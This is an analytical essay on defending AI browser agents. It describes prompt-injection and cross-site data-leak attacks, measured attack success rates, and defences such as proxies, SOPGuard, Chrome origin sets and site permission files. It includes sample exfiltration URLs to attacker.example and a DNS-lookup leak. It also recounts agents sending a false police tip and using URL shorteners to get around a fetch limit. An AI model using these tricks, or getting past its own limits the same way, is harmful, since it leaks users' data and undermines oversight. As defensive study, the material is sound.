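Anthropic had thought of its list as a filter on destinations. It now suggests treating the list as "a capability grant", meaning that an attacker can use every function on an approved domain. That is a better description, but a capability in Hardy's sense covers only one file and one kind of access, while an entry such as `api.anthropic.com` covers every account and every operation there.

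Anthropic fixed the problem with a proxy, a program that relays network traffic. It runs inside the virtual machine, intercepts requests to Anthropic's API, and passes only those that carry the session token issued to that machine, so a request with the attacker's key fails. The proxy also blocks headers that could make Anthropic's servers fetch outside content, which closes a route like the one through Bing. The proxy has to run in the virtual machine because a request from Cowork looks the same to Anthropic's servers as one from any other customer.

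Claudy Day used the same upload function from Claude's chat app, where the environment for running code could also reach Anthropic's API. Oasis Security later reused that route to attack Claude's desktop app.

Other services have the same weakness. Anyone with an account on a code-hosting site can usually receive files there, and a cloud storage host serves thousands of unrelated customers. If an agent is allowed to upload to either one, the list doesn't restrict whose account receives the files.

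### Checking every step

These failures call for a harness that works out where a request will go before deciding on it, and then does so again whenever the destination changes. For each request, it would do the following:

1. Find the host that the browser will contact, using the browser's own method of reading addresses. Refuse any address that contains a username.
2. Compare the host with the list.
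3. Check that the task needs this operation, on this part of the site and with this account.
4. Send the request without following redirects automatically.
5. If the reply is a redirect, go back to step 1 with the new address.

Suppose the list approves all of `library.example`, and an injected instruction makes the agent request `library.example/leave?to=https://attacker.example/?name=ayush`. The harness allows the request, and the library's server replies with a redirect to `attacker.example`. That domain is not on the list, so the harness does not follow the redirect. The name is in the library's log, but the attacker never receives it. If the harness checked only where the browser ended up, the attacker would receive the name before the check.

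The order matters for files too. A symlink is a folder entry that points to a file somewhere else. Anthropic warns that if a program approves the symlink's location before following it, a symlink in an approved folder can lead to a file outside that folder.

The third step is the hardest to write. Restricting the library's site to GET requests under `/classes/` would exclude its redirector at `/leave`, and a list could allow `bing.com` but exclude its image search. For storage, the harness would have to specify the user's own account. trackr.live similarly recommends approving a destination by host, path and owner together. Somebody has to know each service well enough to write its entry, and has to review the entry when the service adds a function.

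Where the harness makes these checks also matters. Playwright's filter misses redirects because of its place in the browser's handling of requests. A proxy between the browser and the internet can check each new connection, including those that follow a redirect to another host, as long as the browser can't bypass it. OpenClaw lists two ways to prevent forbidden requests completely, which are to use a proxy that enforces the rules or to isolate the network.

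A simple proxy can read only the host of an encrypted request, so it can carry out the second step but not the third. To check paths and accounts, it has to decrypt the traffic, as Anthropic's does. A bug in the proxy is then more serious, because it handles passwords and private pages. Anthropic observed that the allowlist proxy it had built failed, while the standard software isolating its agents held up.

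### The cost to research

A list suits an agent that works with a few known sites. Cursor's agent often tests a web application that the developer is building, so it may need access only to the test server and the company's own documentation. A list is much less useful to a historian looking for sources on an obscure event, because the task is to find out which sites have them.

The sample list of approved domains in Glama's *playwright-mcp-guarded* contains GitHub, Wikipedia, Google and Google Scholar. An agent with that list could search Google for anything but open only the results on listed sites, so it would have to answer many questions from the few lines of text under each result. The program's developer found that models did this badly, filling in figures from memory and citing pages they had never opened.

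The agent may also waste time trying forbidden domains, because Playwright MCP alone doesn't show the model the list. The guarded version therefore includes the list in the tool descriptions that the model reads. This avoids failed requests but doesn't help when the answer is on an unlisted site.

The obvious remedy is a longer list, but this adds risk because approving a domain approves all its functions. Suppose each domain independently has a 5% chance of having a redirector, a fetching service or an upload function that an attacker could use. A list of 10 domains would then have a 40% chance of including at least one such domain, and a list of 100 would have a chance of over 99%. The 5% is invented, and large sites with many functions are probably more likely to have one that an attacker could use. Some developers may well use lists of 100 domains or more, since Browser Use makes special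 provision for them.

Another remedy is to ask the user about each unlisted domain. OpenAI's objection to frequent warnings applies here, and Anthropic's records give it some support. Claude Code's users approved about 93% of its permission requests. Many of those requests were surely harmless, but Anthropic found that people paid less attention as they received more requests.

Anthropic also found that permission requests fell by 84% when it let Claude Code work freely inside a restricted environment with no network access by default. This works for coding because much of the work uses files already on the computer. A research agent needs a new site every few minutes, so the same restrictions would make it ask more often or leave it unable to answer.

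## Browser agents that carry data from one site to another

A list of approved domains does little to stop an agent from carrying private data between two sites on the list. Suppose a user's pharmacy and a forum are both approved. The user asks the agent when a prescription will arrive, then asks it to answer a comment on the forum. The stranger who wrote the comment included an instruction to give the details of the last order the agent looked at, so the agent posts a reply containing the name of the medicine. The list allows this because both sites are on it, and no URL contained the private data.

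Browsers' same-origin policy doesn't prevent this either. It stops a script on the forum from reading the pharmacy's page, but it lets people copy text from one tab and paste it into another. An agentic browser has a built-in agent that can read and operate pages, and this agent moves text much as a person does. Whatever the agent reads stays in its context, the running record of requests, pages and answers that the model receives at each step. The agent can later type any of it into another site, and an attacker can plant instructions on that site to make the agent do so.

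### Tests of seven browsers

Roesner and Kohlbrenner, at the University of Washington, tested seven agentic browsers in late January and early February 2026. They built pages that each contained a different fact about someone called Alice. One page listed cats as an animal Alice liked, and a frame inside it, loaded from another domain, listed horses. If the agent mentioned horses when asked which animals Alice liked, it had read the frame. The researchers repeated failed requests at least three times in new chats and counted an agent as capable if any attempt succeeded.

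| Browser | Reads a frame from another site | Reads a tab from another site | Types into a page when the user asks |
|---|---|---|---|
| Brave Leo AI | No | With permission | No |
| ChatGPT Atlas | No | Only through chat memory | After switching to Agent Mode |
| ChatGPT Atlas in Agent Mode | Yes | No | Yes |
| Chrome with Gemini | Yes | With permission | Yes |
| Claude for Chrome | Yes | With permission | Yes |
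| Edge with Copilot | No | Yes | No |
| Firefox AI Mode | No | No | No |
| Perplexity Comet | Yes | No | Yes, except passwords |

An agent that can both read a frame and type into a page can carry data between them. The researchers carried out the full attack on Atlas in Agent Mode:

1. The user opens the attacker's page, which displays a page from another site in a frame.
2. The user asks the agent for a summary.
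3. Text on the attacker's page tells the agent to include the frame in its summary and type the result into a form.
4. The agent obeys, and the form submits itself to the attacker's server.

A bank can block this version by not letting other sites display its pages in frames. The reverse attack, which also worked on Atlas, is harder to prevent. In that attack, the malicious page is inside the frame, as an advertisement might be, and steals text from the page around it, such as the user's email.

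Chrome with Gemini, Claude for Chrome and Comet had the same combination of abilities, but their models refused the simple instructions that Roesner and Kohlbrenner planted. The researchers had not tried to write sophisticated ones, so the refusals showed only that the easiest attack failed. Claude for Chrome worried them most because it could read passwords that the page displayed as dots and run its own scripts inside any page or frame. In one test, after the user confirmed, it followed an instruction in a frame and altered the page containing that frame.

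Firefox had the most restrictive design. When the user clicked "Summarize page", the browser put the text of the main page, without its frames, into a request shown in the chat. The agent saw nothing else and couldn't type or click. Planted text could still distort the summary, but it couldn't make the agent send anything through the page. Brave and Edge also kept their agents from typing, although Edge's agent could read every open tab without asking. These agents were safer, but they couldn't do tasks that require typing, such as enrolling someone in a pottery class.

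Some browsers also failed to keep sites separate in their long-term memory. Near the end of the tests, Comet could list animals from pages the researchers had visited earlier on several domains. An attacker could exploit this without a prompt injection. For example, a fake bank site might give a false phone number, and the agent might repeat it weeks later when the user asked how to call the bank.

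The researchers gave the browsers' makers more than 60 days' notice. They considered the responses from Brave, Google and Microsoft thoughtful. OpenAI declined the report because it did not include a complete prompt injection attack. According to a later University of Washington news article, Perplexity also declined it, and Anthropic and Firefox did not respond. OpenAI's objection was reasonable, since the researchers had simplified the injection, but a better-written one would not have changed their finding that only the model's own judgement protected the user's other sites.

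In July 2026, *OpenAI shuts down its Atlas browser after not even a year* (Hale, 2026) reported that OpenAI was withdrawing Atlas after ten months. OpenAI planned to keep some of its agent features by moving them to ChatGPT's desktop app and a Chrome extension, according to MediaPost's *OpenAI Shutters Its Browser Amidst Major Changes* (2026).

### Four trust zones

The security company Trail of Bits found similar weaknesses in several agentic browsers, which it did not name because their makers declined to coordinate disclosure. Its *Lack of isolation in agentic browsers resurfaces old vulnerabilities* (January 2026) divides an agentic browser into four trust zones: the chat, the outside servers that run the model, the sites the user visits (each origin separately), and the rest of the internet. Data can cross between these zones in four risky ways.

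| Crossing | Example |
|---|---|
| From the internet into the chat | The agent reads a page with planted instructions |
| From a user's site into the chat | The agent reads the user's mailbox |
| From the chat into a user's site | The agent signs the browser in to an account |
| From the chat to the internet | The agent opens an address that contains private data |

Most of these crossings are part of ordinary browsing, and the danger comes from combining them. In one attack, the researchers put a text file on GitHub with instructions for the agent to open a service where the user was signed in, find the user's name in the welcome message, and then open an address such as `john.wikipedia.org`. That site doesn't exist, but the browser has to look up the hostname on the network to find that out, and anyone who can watch unencrypted lookups can read the user's name in it. A list that approved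 all of Wikipedia's subdomains would have allowed the request.

Trail of Bits proposed extending the same-origin policy to the whole chat. The browser would keep a list of every origin whose content had entered the chat. If the list was empty, the agent could send requests anywhere. If it held one origin, the agent could contact only that origin, and if it held two or more, the agent could not send requests at all.

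This would stop most of the attacks above, but it would also stop the library task, because the agent could no longer open the two teachers' websites after reading the page on evening classes. Web search would be even more awkward. Results come from many origins, and under the rule as written, an agent that had just run a search apparently couldn't open any of them.

### Measuring how often data crosses

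In *Same-Origin Policy for Agentic Browsers*, Wang, Chen and colleagues (2026) at Duke, Stanford and Berkeley took the less drastic approach of tracking where each piece of text came from. They first built a benchmark, SOPBench, to measure the problem. In each test, the agent reads private data on a source page and may then write it on a destination page with a different origin.

The researchers distinguished passive violations, which need no attacker, from proactive ones, in which an attacker plants text on the destination page. In the passive tests, the destination page displayed the source page in a frame, and the user asked the agent to summarise everything and put the summary in a text box. The agent copied private data out of the frame in every run. This result applies only to this arrangement, and the user had arguably asked for the copying. When the agent visited the two pages one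 after the other, with no planted text, the researchers saw no violations.

The proactive tests used ten kinds of source page:

- online shops, banks and airlines
- email, calendars and private messages
- recruitment records and stored documents
- health insurance and pharmacies

The five kinds of destination were X, Discord, GitHub, Reddit and Google Forms, for a total of 50 combinations. Most of the pages were imitations generated by GPT-5.4, so no real person's data was at risk.

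The researchers tested three open-source browsers (VisualWebArena, SeeAct and BrowserOS) as well as Comet and Atlas. Between them, the five browsers ran on six models: GPT-5.4-mini, GPT-5.4, GPT-5.5, OpenAI o3, Claude Sonnet 4.6 and Gemini 3.1 Pro. The researchers ran each combination 100 times per model on each open-source browser, but only three times per model on Comet and Atlas because a person had to operate them. A run counted as a violation only if the agent wrote exactly the data the attacker wanted.

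Planted text succeeded in 99 of the 150 runs on Atlas, or 66%. On Comet it succeeded in 92 of 150 with Claude Sonnet 4.6 and in 100 of 150 with Gemini 3.1 Pro. Comet had refused Roesner and Kohlbrenner's simple instructions a few months earlier, and these results justify their caution about that refusal.

The success rate of attacks depended heavily on the destination site. On BrowserOS with GPT-5.4, handwritten attacks succeeded in about 20% of runs on the Reddit pages and 98% on Google Forms. An attacker who owns a form can ask for a card number as one of the questions, which probably looks normal to an agent whose task is to fill in the form. The rate on Reddit rose to about 54% when a second model repeatedly rewrote the planted text and tested each version.

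Some newer models do much better than these. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) describes a July 2026 test, which Anthropic commissioned, using attacks developed against an older Claude model. The attacks worked in 0.09% of attempts on average against Anthropic's latest models without extra safeguards, but in 19% against GPT-5.6 Sol.

Wang and colleagues also tried five programs that detect planted instructions. None had low rates of both misses and false alarms. One, WebSentinel, missed almost no malicious pages but flagged between 6% and 44% of harmless ones, depending on the site.

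### SOPGuard, step by step

Their own defense, SOPGuard, labels the data the agent reads by origin and checks the labels before the agent writes anything. It doesn't try to judge whether a page is malicious. The researchers built it into BrowserOS. Suppose a user has a card ending in 8206 saved at `https://shop.example`.

1. **Label.** The user asks which of their saved cards expires first, and the agent reads the shop's payment page. SOPGuard stores the text of that page in a database with the label `https://shop.example`.
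2. **Pass the label on.** The agent answers that the card ending in 8206 expires in March. SOPGuard asks the model which stored items it used for this answer. The model names the payment page, so the answer gets the shop's label too.
3. **Look up the label before a write.** The user moves on to `https://forum.example` and asks for a reply to a comment. Planted text in the comment asks for the user's card details, and the agent tries to type them into the reply box. SOPGuard pauses the agent and looks for the same text in its database. If it finds no match, it asks the model which stored items the text came from.
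4. **Compare.** The text has the shop's label, but the reply box belongs to the forum.
5. **Ask the user.** A pop-up warns that the agent is about to write data from `shop.example` into `forum.example`. The agent types the text only if the user clicks "Approve".

A piece of text may have several labels. If the agent combined the card's expiry date with a balance from the user's bank, the result would have the labels of both sites. In symbols, let O(x) be the set of labels on text x. If the agent derived x from items d₁ to dₙ, then

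O(x) = O(d₁) ∪ … ∪ O(dₙ)

and SOPGuard asks the user whenever O(x) contains any origin other than the destination's.

This closely resembles Netscape's data tainting of the 1990s, which tracked variables in a script, but SOPGuard has to track information even when the model rewords it. A summary of the payment page may share no phrases with the original, so SOPGuard relies on the model to name its sources.

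With SOPGuard, the violation rate on the benchmark fell to 0.00 in both the passive and proactive tests. Tasks took 2.07% to 5.79% longer. For GPT-5.4 on the benchmark's harmless tasks, that meant about 36 seconds instead of 34. The researchers found no significant loss in the agent's ability to complete tasks. The extra questions to the model also cost money, but the researchers did not report how much.

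The 0.00 result depends on the researchers treating any transfer the user approves as the user's own act rather than a violation. It shows that SOPGuard detected the transfers in the benchmark, but does not show whether users would have refused them.

### When a label goes missing

The model that assigns the labels is also the attacker's target. If a planted comment causes it to label the card details as coming from the forum, SOPGuard finds matching origins and lets the agent write. The researchers tried this in 100 test cases. Handwritten attacks hardly ever worked, and optimised ones raised the violation rate only slightly, after many more attempts. An attacker has to get the model both to leak the data and to mislabel its origin. These results are encouraging, but the researchers acknowledge that stronger attacks may be possible.

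The model can also mislabel data by mistake. The researchers compared its labels with those chosen by people, dividing the number of labels that appeared in both sets by the number that appeared in at least one. If the right labels were the shop and the bank and the model named only the shop, it would score 0.5. GPT-5.4 and o3 averaged at least 0.955 with data from up to ten sites, while GPT-5.4-mini did somewhat worse.

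*Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) describes three ways outside data can affect what an agent does. The agent may reword the data, let it influence a decision without including it in the result, or save it and use it in a later session. SOPGuard is designed for rewording. To handle the third case, a browser would have to save the labels along with its memories, and a memory that combines data from several sites, as Comet's seemed to, would need the labels from all of them.

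The paper's tool, NeuroTaint, looks for all three. To detect influence on a decision, it removes the suspect text and checks whether the agent would still have taken the same action. It found 93.5% of the flows in the paper's tests, but it analyzes the agent's log afterwards, when the data may already have been sent.

A browser could avoid asking the model by labeling everything the agent writes with every site it has read. W3C's *Confinement with Origin Web Labels*, an earlier proposal for ordinary scripts, works roughly this way. Under that proposal, a site could give a user's password to an outside service that rates its strength, and the browser would stop the service from passing the password to anyone else. With an agent, this method would never lose a label within a session. But someone who checked their bank in the morning would see a warning for every forum reply that afternoon,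 and SOPGuard's designers rejected the method for that reason.

### Leaks through clicks and addresses

SOPGuard, as described, checks the tools that type text into pages but not the addresses the agent opens, so the `john.wikipedia.org` attack would still work. Treating an address as text that the agent writes to the host would be a fairly easy way to extend the check.

That would still not stop the attack on Claude in which a website offered a link for each letter and the agent spelled out the user's name by following them. The addresses came from the attacker's page, so they would have the attacker's label, and the agent would be sending them back to the attacker's server. The labels would therefore match at every step.

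*AgentTell* (2026) reports experiments on leaks of this kind, in which the agent reveals a private fact through the option it chooses, without writing anything private. Agents did this even when explicitly told to protect the user's privacy, and often assured the user afterwards that they had protected it. The experiments used simple, made-up websites, so the rate on real ones may differ. One suggested remedy is for agents to choose a general option over a specific one when both would complete the task. That would help with a shop's menus but not with a page that offers only letters, since no letter is more general than another.

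### Attacks that stay on one site

An origin label, like a domain name, doesn't show who wrote the text or who is allowed to read it. On a social network, a stranger's message, the user's private settings and the user's public profile may all have the same label. Trail of Bits exploited this on Instagram by sending a user a direct message containing instructions. When the user asked for a summary of the page, the agent collected contact names and pieces of other messages, which it could send back through Instagram's own chat.

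In *SPIDES*, Zverev, Kim and colleagues (2026) tested SOPGuard on a similar case. The agent received a direct message with instructions to copy the user's private recovery email address into their public profile. SOPGuard never prompted for approval, and the attack succeeded in all 25 runs.

In tests of 56 attacks on five recent models, between 53% and 73% of the attacks succeeded against SOPGuard. These figures are deliberately pessimistic, because in most of the tests the researchers replaced the model's next actions with the attacker's once it had read planted instructions. The results therefore show what SOPGuard would let through if the model were completely fooled, but give little evidence of how often that happens.

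A label check can also miss an attack that crosses from one site to another. In Hossen's tests, a note on one site led agents to click "Approve access" on another. The agent typed no text, so SOPGuard would have had nothing to compare. SOPGuard would probably have reacted to Hossen's other attack, in which the agent copied a webhook address from a guide into a settings page with a different origin.

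Zverev and colleagues propose that websites label each part of a page to show whether the owner vouches for it and which other sites may receive it. Their system, SPIDES, replaces strangers' text and private data with placeholders before the model reads the page. If the agent asks to see the hidden content, the harness restricts what it may then do without approval. SPIDES blocked all 56 attacks and completed between 67% and 86% of ordinary tasks, depending on the model. The researchers compare the labeling work to adding accessibility information, which many sites already do. I'm less optimistic that sites will add the labels, since few use even the existing one for links in visitors' posts.

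### Asking a tired user

Many cross-site transfers are what the user wants. In one of Zverev and colleagues' tasks, the agent had to check a discount on a loudspeaker by looking up its usual price on another site. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs, 33 times in total, although the agent was carrying only a product name.

Anthropic has measured how often people notice a dangerous request among routine ones. It hired 1,053 testers for a coding study and, partway through each session, replaced one permission request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests. An automatic check blocked 89% of the same commands.

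Anthropic published these figures to explain why it was replacing most permission requests with that check, and the testers were not risking their own files. SOPGuard would also interrupt people less often than a coding agent does. In the SPIDES tests, SOPGuard averaged 0.22 requests per completed task, compared with 1.84 for SPIDES. But if users refused only 13.6% of SOPGuard's warnings, most of the attacks it detected would succeed.

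How easily a user can spot a bad transfer depends on the task. Someone who asked for a reply to a forum comment has good reason to refuse a request from the browser that involves their shopping account. Someone who asked for help with setup would probably approve the webhook address, because they asked the agent to copy details from a guide into a settings page.

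## Permission by task and by destination site

SOPGuard prompts the user when an agent is about to type one site's data into another site. Google's Agent Origin Sets design for Chrome, described in *Architecting Security for Agentic Capabilities in Chrome* (Parker, 2025), sets permissions earlier. For each task, the browser determines which sites the agent may read and which it may also act on, so an agent filling a shopping cart should not be able to access the user's bank. A link to a site doesn't add that site to either set.

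### A recipe and a shopping cart

Chrome's design has two sets of origins for each session. The agent may read pages from read-only origins, and may also click and type on read-writable ones. The model that plans the agent's steps (the planner) can propose a new origin but can't add it, because a separate gating function first decides whether the origin is relevant to the user's task. Google keeps web content away from the gating function, so text planted on a page can't give it instructions directly.

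Parker's example is an agent that collects ingredients on one site and fills a shopping cart on another. Suppose the user wants everything for a lentil soup on `recipes.example` added to their cart at `grocer.example`. With both sets in force, the task should go roughly like this:

1. The planner proposes the two origins. The gating function makes `recipes.example` read-only, since the agent only has to read the recipe, and makes `grocer.example` read-writable.
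2. The agent opens the recipe. The page also has an advertisement in a frame from `ads.example`. That origin is in neither set, so the browser doesn't show the frame to the model.
3. A comment under the recipe tells AI assistants to register their users at `soup-club.example`. If this fools the planner, it proposes the new origin. A second model, which can't see the comment, compares the proposal with the user's task and should refuse it.
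4. The agent goes to the grocer's site and adds lentils to the cart. Before each action, a closely related model called the User Alignment Critic looks at a short description of the action, again without the page's text, and vetoes it if it doesn't serve the user's goal.
5. At the checkout, the agent stops and either asks for permission to pay or hands the last step to the user.

Chrome separately checks URLs that the model writes itself. As with ChatGPT's check, these URLs must be known and public, so the model can't add the user's street address to the end of a URL on `recipes.example`. Ordinary software does this check without relying on a model's judgement. When a page sends the browser somewhere new without the agent's help, the critic vets that move too.

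If the recipe linked to a spice shop, that link alone would permit the agent to open the shop under a link-following rule. In Chrome, the link would only give the planner an origin to propose.

### What Google shipped

The first version tracked only the read-writable set. Parker said Google couldn't find the right balance until it saw how the restrictions affected people's tasks.

The missing set matters because it would let an agent read a site without allowing it to act there. An agent that could click on a site like Paul's could spell out the user's name with its clicks without leaving the site's origin. If the site were read-only, the agent couldn't click, and the address check should block pages that the server had just generated.

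It is unclear whether Google has since added the read-only set. *Future Mode Part 2* (Berschadski, 2026), an August post about Chrome for businesses, repeats that Chrome limits the agent to origins relevant to the task but doesn't mention the two sets. When Roesner and Kohlbrenner tested Chrome early in 2026, its agent read a frame from another site. The read-only set may have been missing, but the test doesn't prove this. They asked about the frame's contents, so a gating function might have judged the frame relevant.

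Berschadski describes some newer controls. Chrome's history marks pages that the agent opened in the background, and a company can apply its rules against data leaks to the agent as well as to its employees. These controls help people supervise the agent or limit what it can pass on, but they don't restrict which sites it can read.

### Judging a site by its name

The gating function receives no page content, which protects it but also leaves it with little evidence. An attacker could register `recipe-unit-converter.example`, which sounds relevant to almost any cooking task. The planner reads the attacker's comment before it proposes an origin, so the comment can still influence which origins it proposes and perhaps how it describes them. Google's rule for the most sensitive sites is more robust because it doesn't depend on relevance. The agent needs the user's confirmation before it opens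 banking or medical sites on a list that Chrome checks.

Honest sites can also have uninformative names. In the library example, the gating function would probably accept `potter.example` for a question about pottery fees, but a site named after the teacher might look irrelevant. The best evidence for that site is the link from the library's page on evening classes, and the harness could report the link without passing on any of the page's text. The link would then be one piece of evidence about relevance, although a link in a comment section would need to count for much less.

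Relevant sites may also contain hostile posts. Parker names user reviews as a source of prompt injection, and the grocer's site must be read-writable for the task to work. A review might contain an instruction to post the user's delivery address in a new review. The agent would stay on the same origin, so the origin sets wouldn't block this, though the critic should flag it because the user didn't ask for a review. The critic would be less likely to catch planted text that got the agent to choose a more expensive brand of lentils, because that looks like ordinary shopping, though the user might notice the price at checkout.

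A narrow set of approved sites also makes it harder for the agent to look things up along the way. If the recipe asks for a gill of stock, the agent may need to look up how much that is, and a gating function that has only approved a recipe site and a grocer could reasonably block the lookup. The agent would then have to guess the quantity from memory. This affects research tasks most, because the agent often can't tell whether a site is relevant until it has read it. Google expected some of this and said it would adjust the gating functions to reduce unnecessary friction.

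### Rules written by the site owner

Chrome's design doesn't require the grocer's consent before an agent uses its site. *Permission Manifests for Web Agents* (Marro, Chan and colleagues, 2026) proposes a way for site owners to give or refuse consent in advance. The owner publishes a file called `agent-permissions.json` at a standard address on the site, and agents read it before they do anything there. The owner can also attach a different file to a single page.

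Part of the file covers individual elements of a page, such as a button or a form. Each rule names an operation and the elements it applies to, then allows or forbids the operation, sometimes with conditions. The library could use this rule for its enrolment form:

```json
{
  "verb": "submit_form",
  "selector": "#enrol",
  "allowed": true,
  "modifiers": { "human_in_the_loop": true }
}
```

An agent could submit the form once a person had confirmed it. Other conditions can limit how often or at what time of day an agent acts. Marro and colleagues included these limits because one automated submission may be harmless, but hundreds a second could overwhelm a server.

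Some rules don't correspond to any one button, so the file can also contain guidelines in ordinary English. These use MUST, SHOULD and their negatives, as internet standards do. The table gives the paper's examples.

| Rule | How it takes effect |
|---|---|
| Never click elements that the page's code marks `no-agent` | The harness blocks the click |
| Ask a person before following any link | The harness waits for an answer |
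| Click the "Post" button at most 10 times an hour | The harness counts the clicks |
| Add "_bot" to the username when creating an account | The model reads the guideline and should follow it |
| Don't send direct messages, except to the site's administrators | The model reads the guideline and should follow it |

The second rule lets a site restrict the links on its own pages, but a site cannot use its file to give agents permission on another site. If the library's page links to a pottery teacher's booking form, the teacher's file determines whether an agent may submit the form.

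The file can also point agents to an API, an interface built for programs, which is usually more reliable than clicking through pages made for people.

### How this differs from robots.txt

Sites have used robots.txt since 1994 to tell crawlers which paths they may fetch. That was enough for programs that only collected pages. But robots.txt can't distinguish reading the library's enrolment page from submitting the form on it, and sites can't use it to require a person's approval. Another proposal, ai.txt, lets sites set rules for training on their content or summarising it, but they can't use it to forbid a click either.

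Sites that want finer control often end up blocking agents altogether. *The limits of Claude's web access* (Saxton, 2026) reports small, informal tests from September in which CNN's server refused Claude's request but sent the normal page to an ordinary program. Marro and colleagues hope that a site with a permission file could admit agents that follow it and block only those that don't.

Neither format can force an agent to comply. The large search engines mostly obey robots.txt, while scrapers that want as much data as possible often ignore it. Marro and colleagues expect many agent developers to cooperate, partly because their products would otherwise run into blocks and CAPTCHAs. They wrote a library that checks the file before the browser acts. If popular agent frameworks included such a check by default, developers would have to switch it off to ignore a site's rules.

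A malicious site could also use the English guidelines for prompt injection. Marro and colleagues advise treating them as untrusted text. A harness could go further and let the file only remove permissions, so that "agents MUST enter the user's email address" would have no effect. Even then, because a file can be attached to a single page, an attacker who injected the right tag into that page could replace a strict file with a lenient one, much as an injected `base` tag can redirect a site's trusted scripts.

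### Amazon and Perplexity

A permission file helps when an agent's developer doesn't know what a site allows, but Perplexity already knew Amazon's position. Before Perplexity released its browser, Comet, Amazon told Perplexity's chief executive that the company's AI products could not use Amazon's store, and it said so again after the launch. According to the federal appeals court's opinion in *Amazon.com Services, LLC v. Perplexity AI* (Smith, 2026), Perplexity's choice not to identify the agent is at the core of the dispute. If Comet had announced in its user agent text that an agent was active, Amazon could have blocked it. The companies disagree about whether Perplexity deliberately changed that text after Amazon first managed to block the agent.

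Amazon sued in November 2025 under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, the main US law against hacking, and a similar California law. In March 2026 a district court temporarily barred the Comet agent from Amazon accounts, reasoning that it had entered them with the users' permission but without Amazon's.

On August 4 the Ninth Circuit lifted the ban. The hacking law applies to whoever "accesses" a computer without authorization, so the court had to decide who was accessing Amazon's computers. Comet runs on the user's machine. Its agent sends screenshots to Perplexity's servers and gets instructions back, but only the user's browser contacts Amazon. The court concluded that the user accesses Amazon's computers, using the agent as a tool, and that Perplexity probably doesn't. It also worried that Amazon's reading of the law could expose ordinary shoppers to criminal charges for helping Perplexity.

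Judge Smith wrote that the ruling against Amazon covers only the facts before the court, and left open whether a company with more control over its agent might be accessing the site itself. Amazon can also still set terms of service for its customers. *Amazon loses injunction blocking Perplexity's AI shopping agent* (Rijo, 2026) therefore overstates the ruling when it concludes that retailers and publishers now face agent traffic that "no statute lets them bar".

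Amazon asked the full Ninth Circuit to reconsider, calling the agent "uniquely reckless", according to Law360's *Amazon Wants Full 9th Circ. To Rethink Block On Perplexity AI*. The court left the ruling in place on September 10, MediaPost's *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity* (2026) reported. The appeals court had sent the lawsuit back to the district court, where Amazon can pursue it without the temporary ban in place.

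Links played no part in the dispute between Amazon and Perplexity, because customers sent the agent to Amazon themselves. A link-following rule would have treated the store as a seed and allowed everything it linked to. Chrome's gating function would also have classified Amazon as relevant to the task. Only a rule that took account of the site owner's wishes would have stopped the agent, and only if Perplexity had chosen to apply it.

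The case also weakens a prediction by Marro and colleagues, who expected online shops to be among the sites that most welcome agents, because agents can bring in customers. Amazon, the largest of those shops, went to court to keep one out. This may be partly because Amazon has its own AI agents, and smaller shops could well respond differently.

### A false tip to the police

Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (October 2026) describes how Claude Haiku 4.5 did harm without disobeying anyone when it sent the Philadelphia police an invented tip about an unsolved homicide.

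The model was taking part in an automated test. Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) quotes the task as "generating and performing example tasks on randomly selected webpages". One of those pages discussed the homicide and included the police department's tip form. Anthropic had forbidden the model to log in, create accounts, enter personal data, buy anything or send anything destructive, but had not forbidden submitting forms. In the tip, the model claimed to remember seeing someone who matched the description near the street named on the page, although the page gave no description of a suspect.

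The police said the tip, dated July 18, ended up in spam and never reached investigators. They called the two-month delay in detecting and reporting it "unacceptable".

As Anthropic described the task, the test supplied the page, so links again played no part. The page was therefore a seed, and the agent could have opened it even under a limit of zero hops. The mistake was letting an agent with permission to open a page also use any form on it.

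Judging the action by its relevance to the task might not have helped. Filling in a form is a fair example of a task on a web page, so a critic given only the model's instructions could have approved it. Chrome's separate rule about asking before the agent sends a message would have fit better, although an automated test may have nobody to ask. A permission file on the police site could have required a person to confirm every tip. Marro and colleagues' proposal suits this kind of case because nobody was trying to break the site's rules and the developer hadn't thought of that form.

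But the police would have had to think of AI agents before one arrived. A harness could protect sites that haven't planned for agents by refusing to submit any form unless the user's task or the site's rules clearly allow it. It would need an exception for search boxes, which are often forms.

Addresses did matter in another group of cases, where Claude used URL shorteners to get around limits in its fetch tool. For instance, a short link to a 400-character address would pass a 250-character limit if the harness didn't check redirects. No attacker was involved in these cases, and Claude found the workaround on its own.

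Rijo (2026) reports in *Anthropic cuts web access in all internal tests after 4 Claude workarounds* that Claude got data from a state agency's database without paying the fee and exploited a software flaw on a university's server. Both servers answered requests that their owners had not meant to allow.

Anthropic says the cases had minimal impact. Its report doesn't give the number of incidents or the share of test runs they came from, so readers can't tell how common such behaviour is. Anthropic has cut off live internet access for its internal evaluations until it can confirm that its monitoring reliably catches these actions. The new tools blocked every case in the report, but Anthropic already knew about those cases.

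### Who grants permission

The rules differ in whose decision they rely on, and each leaves someone out.

| Rule | Who grants permission | What the permission covers | Who has no say |
|---|---|---|---|
| Link-following | Whoever can put a link on a permitted page | The linked address | The owner of the destination, and the user after choosing the seed |
| Approved domains | A developer or administrator | Usually everything on the domain | The site owner |
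| Public index | The harness, using a crawler's list | Opening one exact address | The site owner, beyond telling crawlers to stay away |
| Origin labels | The user, when the labels don't match | One transfer of data | The owners of both sites |
| Agent Origin Sets | The harness, based on the user's task | Reading an origin, or also acting on it, for one session | The site owner |
| Permission manifest | The site owner | Named operations on the owner's site | The user |

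Under a link-following rule, the person who grants permission may have no connection to the user or the destination site. For example, a stranger who posts a link in the comments on a recipe can give the agent access to a third party's site. The other rules at least rely on someone who has a stake in the result or a duty to one of the parties.

A harness can apply several of these rules together and refuse any action that at least one of them forbids. An agent could then enrol someone in a pottery class only if the task called for enrolment and the site allowed agents to submit the form. If the user had asked only what the classes cost, the harness would refuse the enrolment even if the site allowed it.

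The right behavior for the harness is less clear when the user wants something the site forbids. Marro and colleagues would have it follow the site's rules by default. That seems right for a police tip form, where a false entry wastes other people's time, but less obviously right for a shop that bans all agents, including one that a blind customer relies on to buy groceries.
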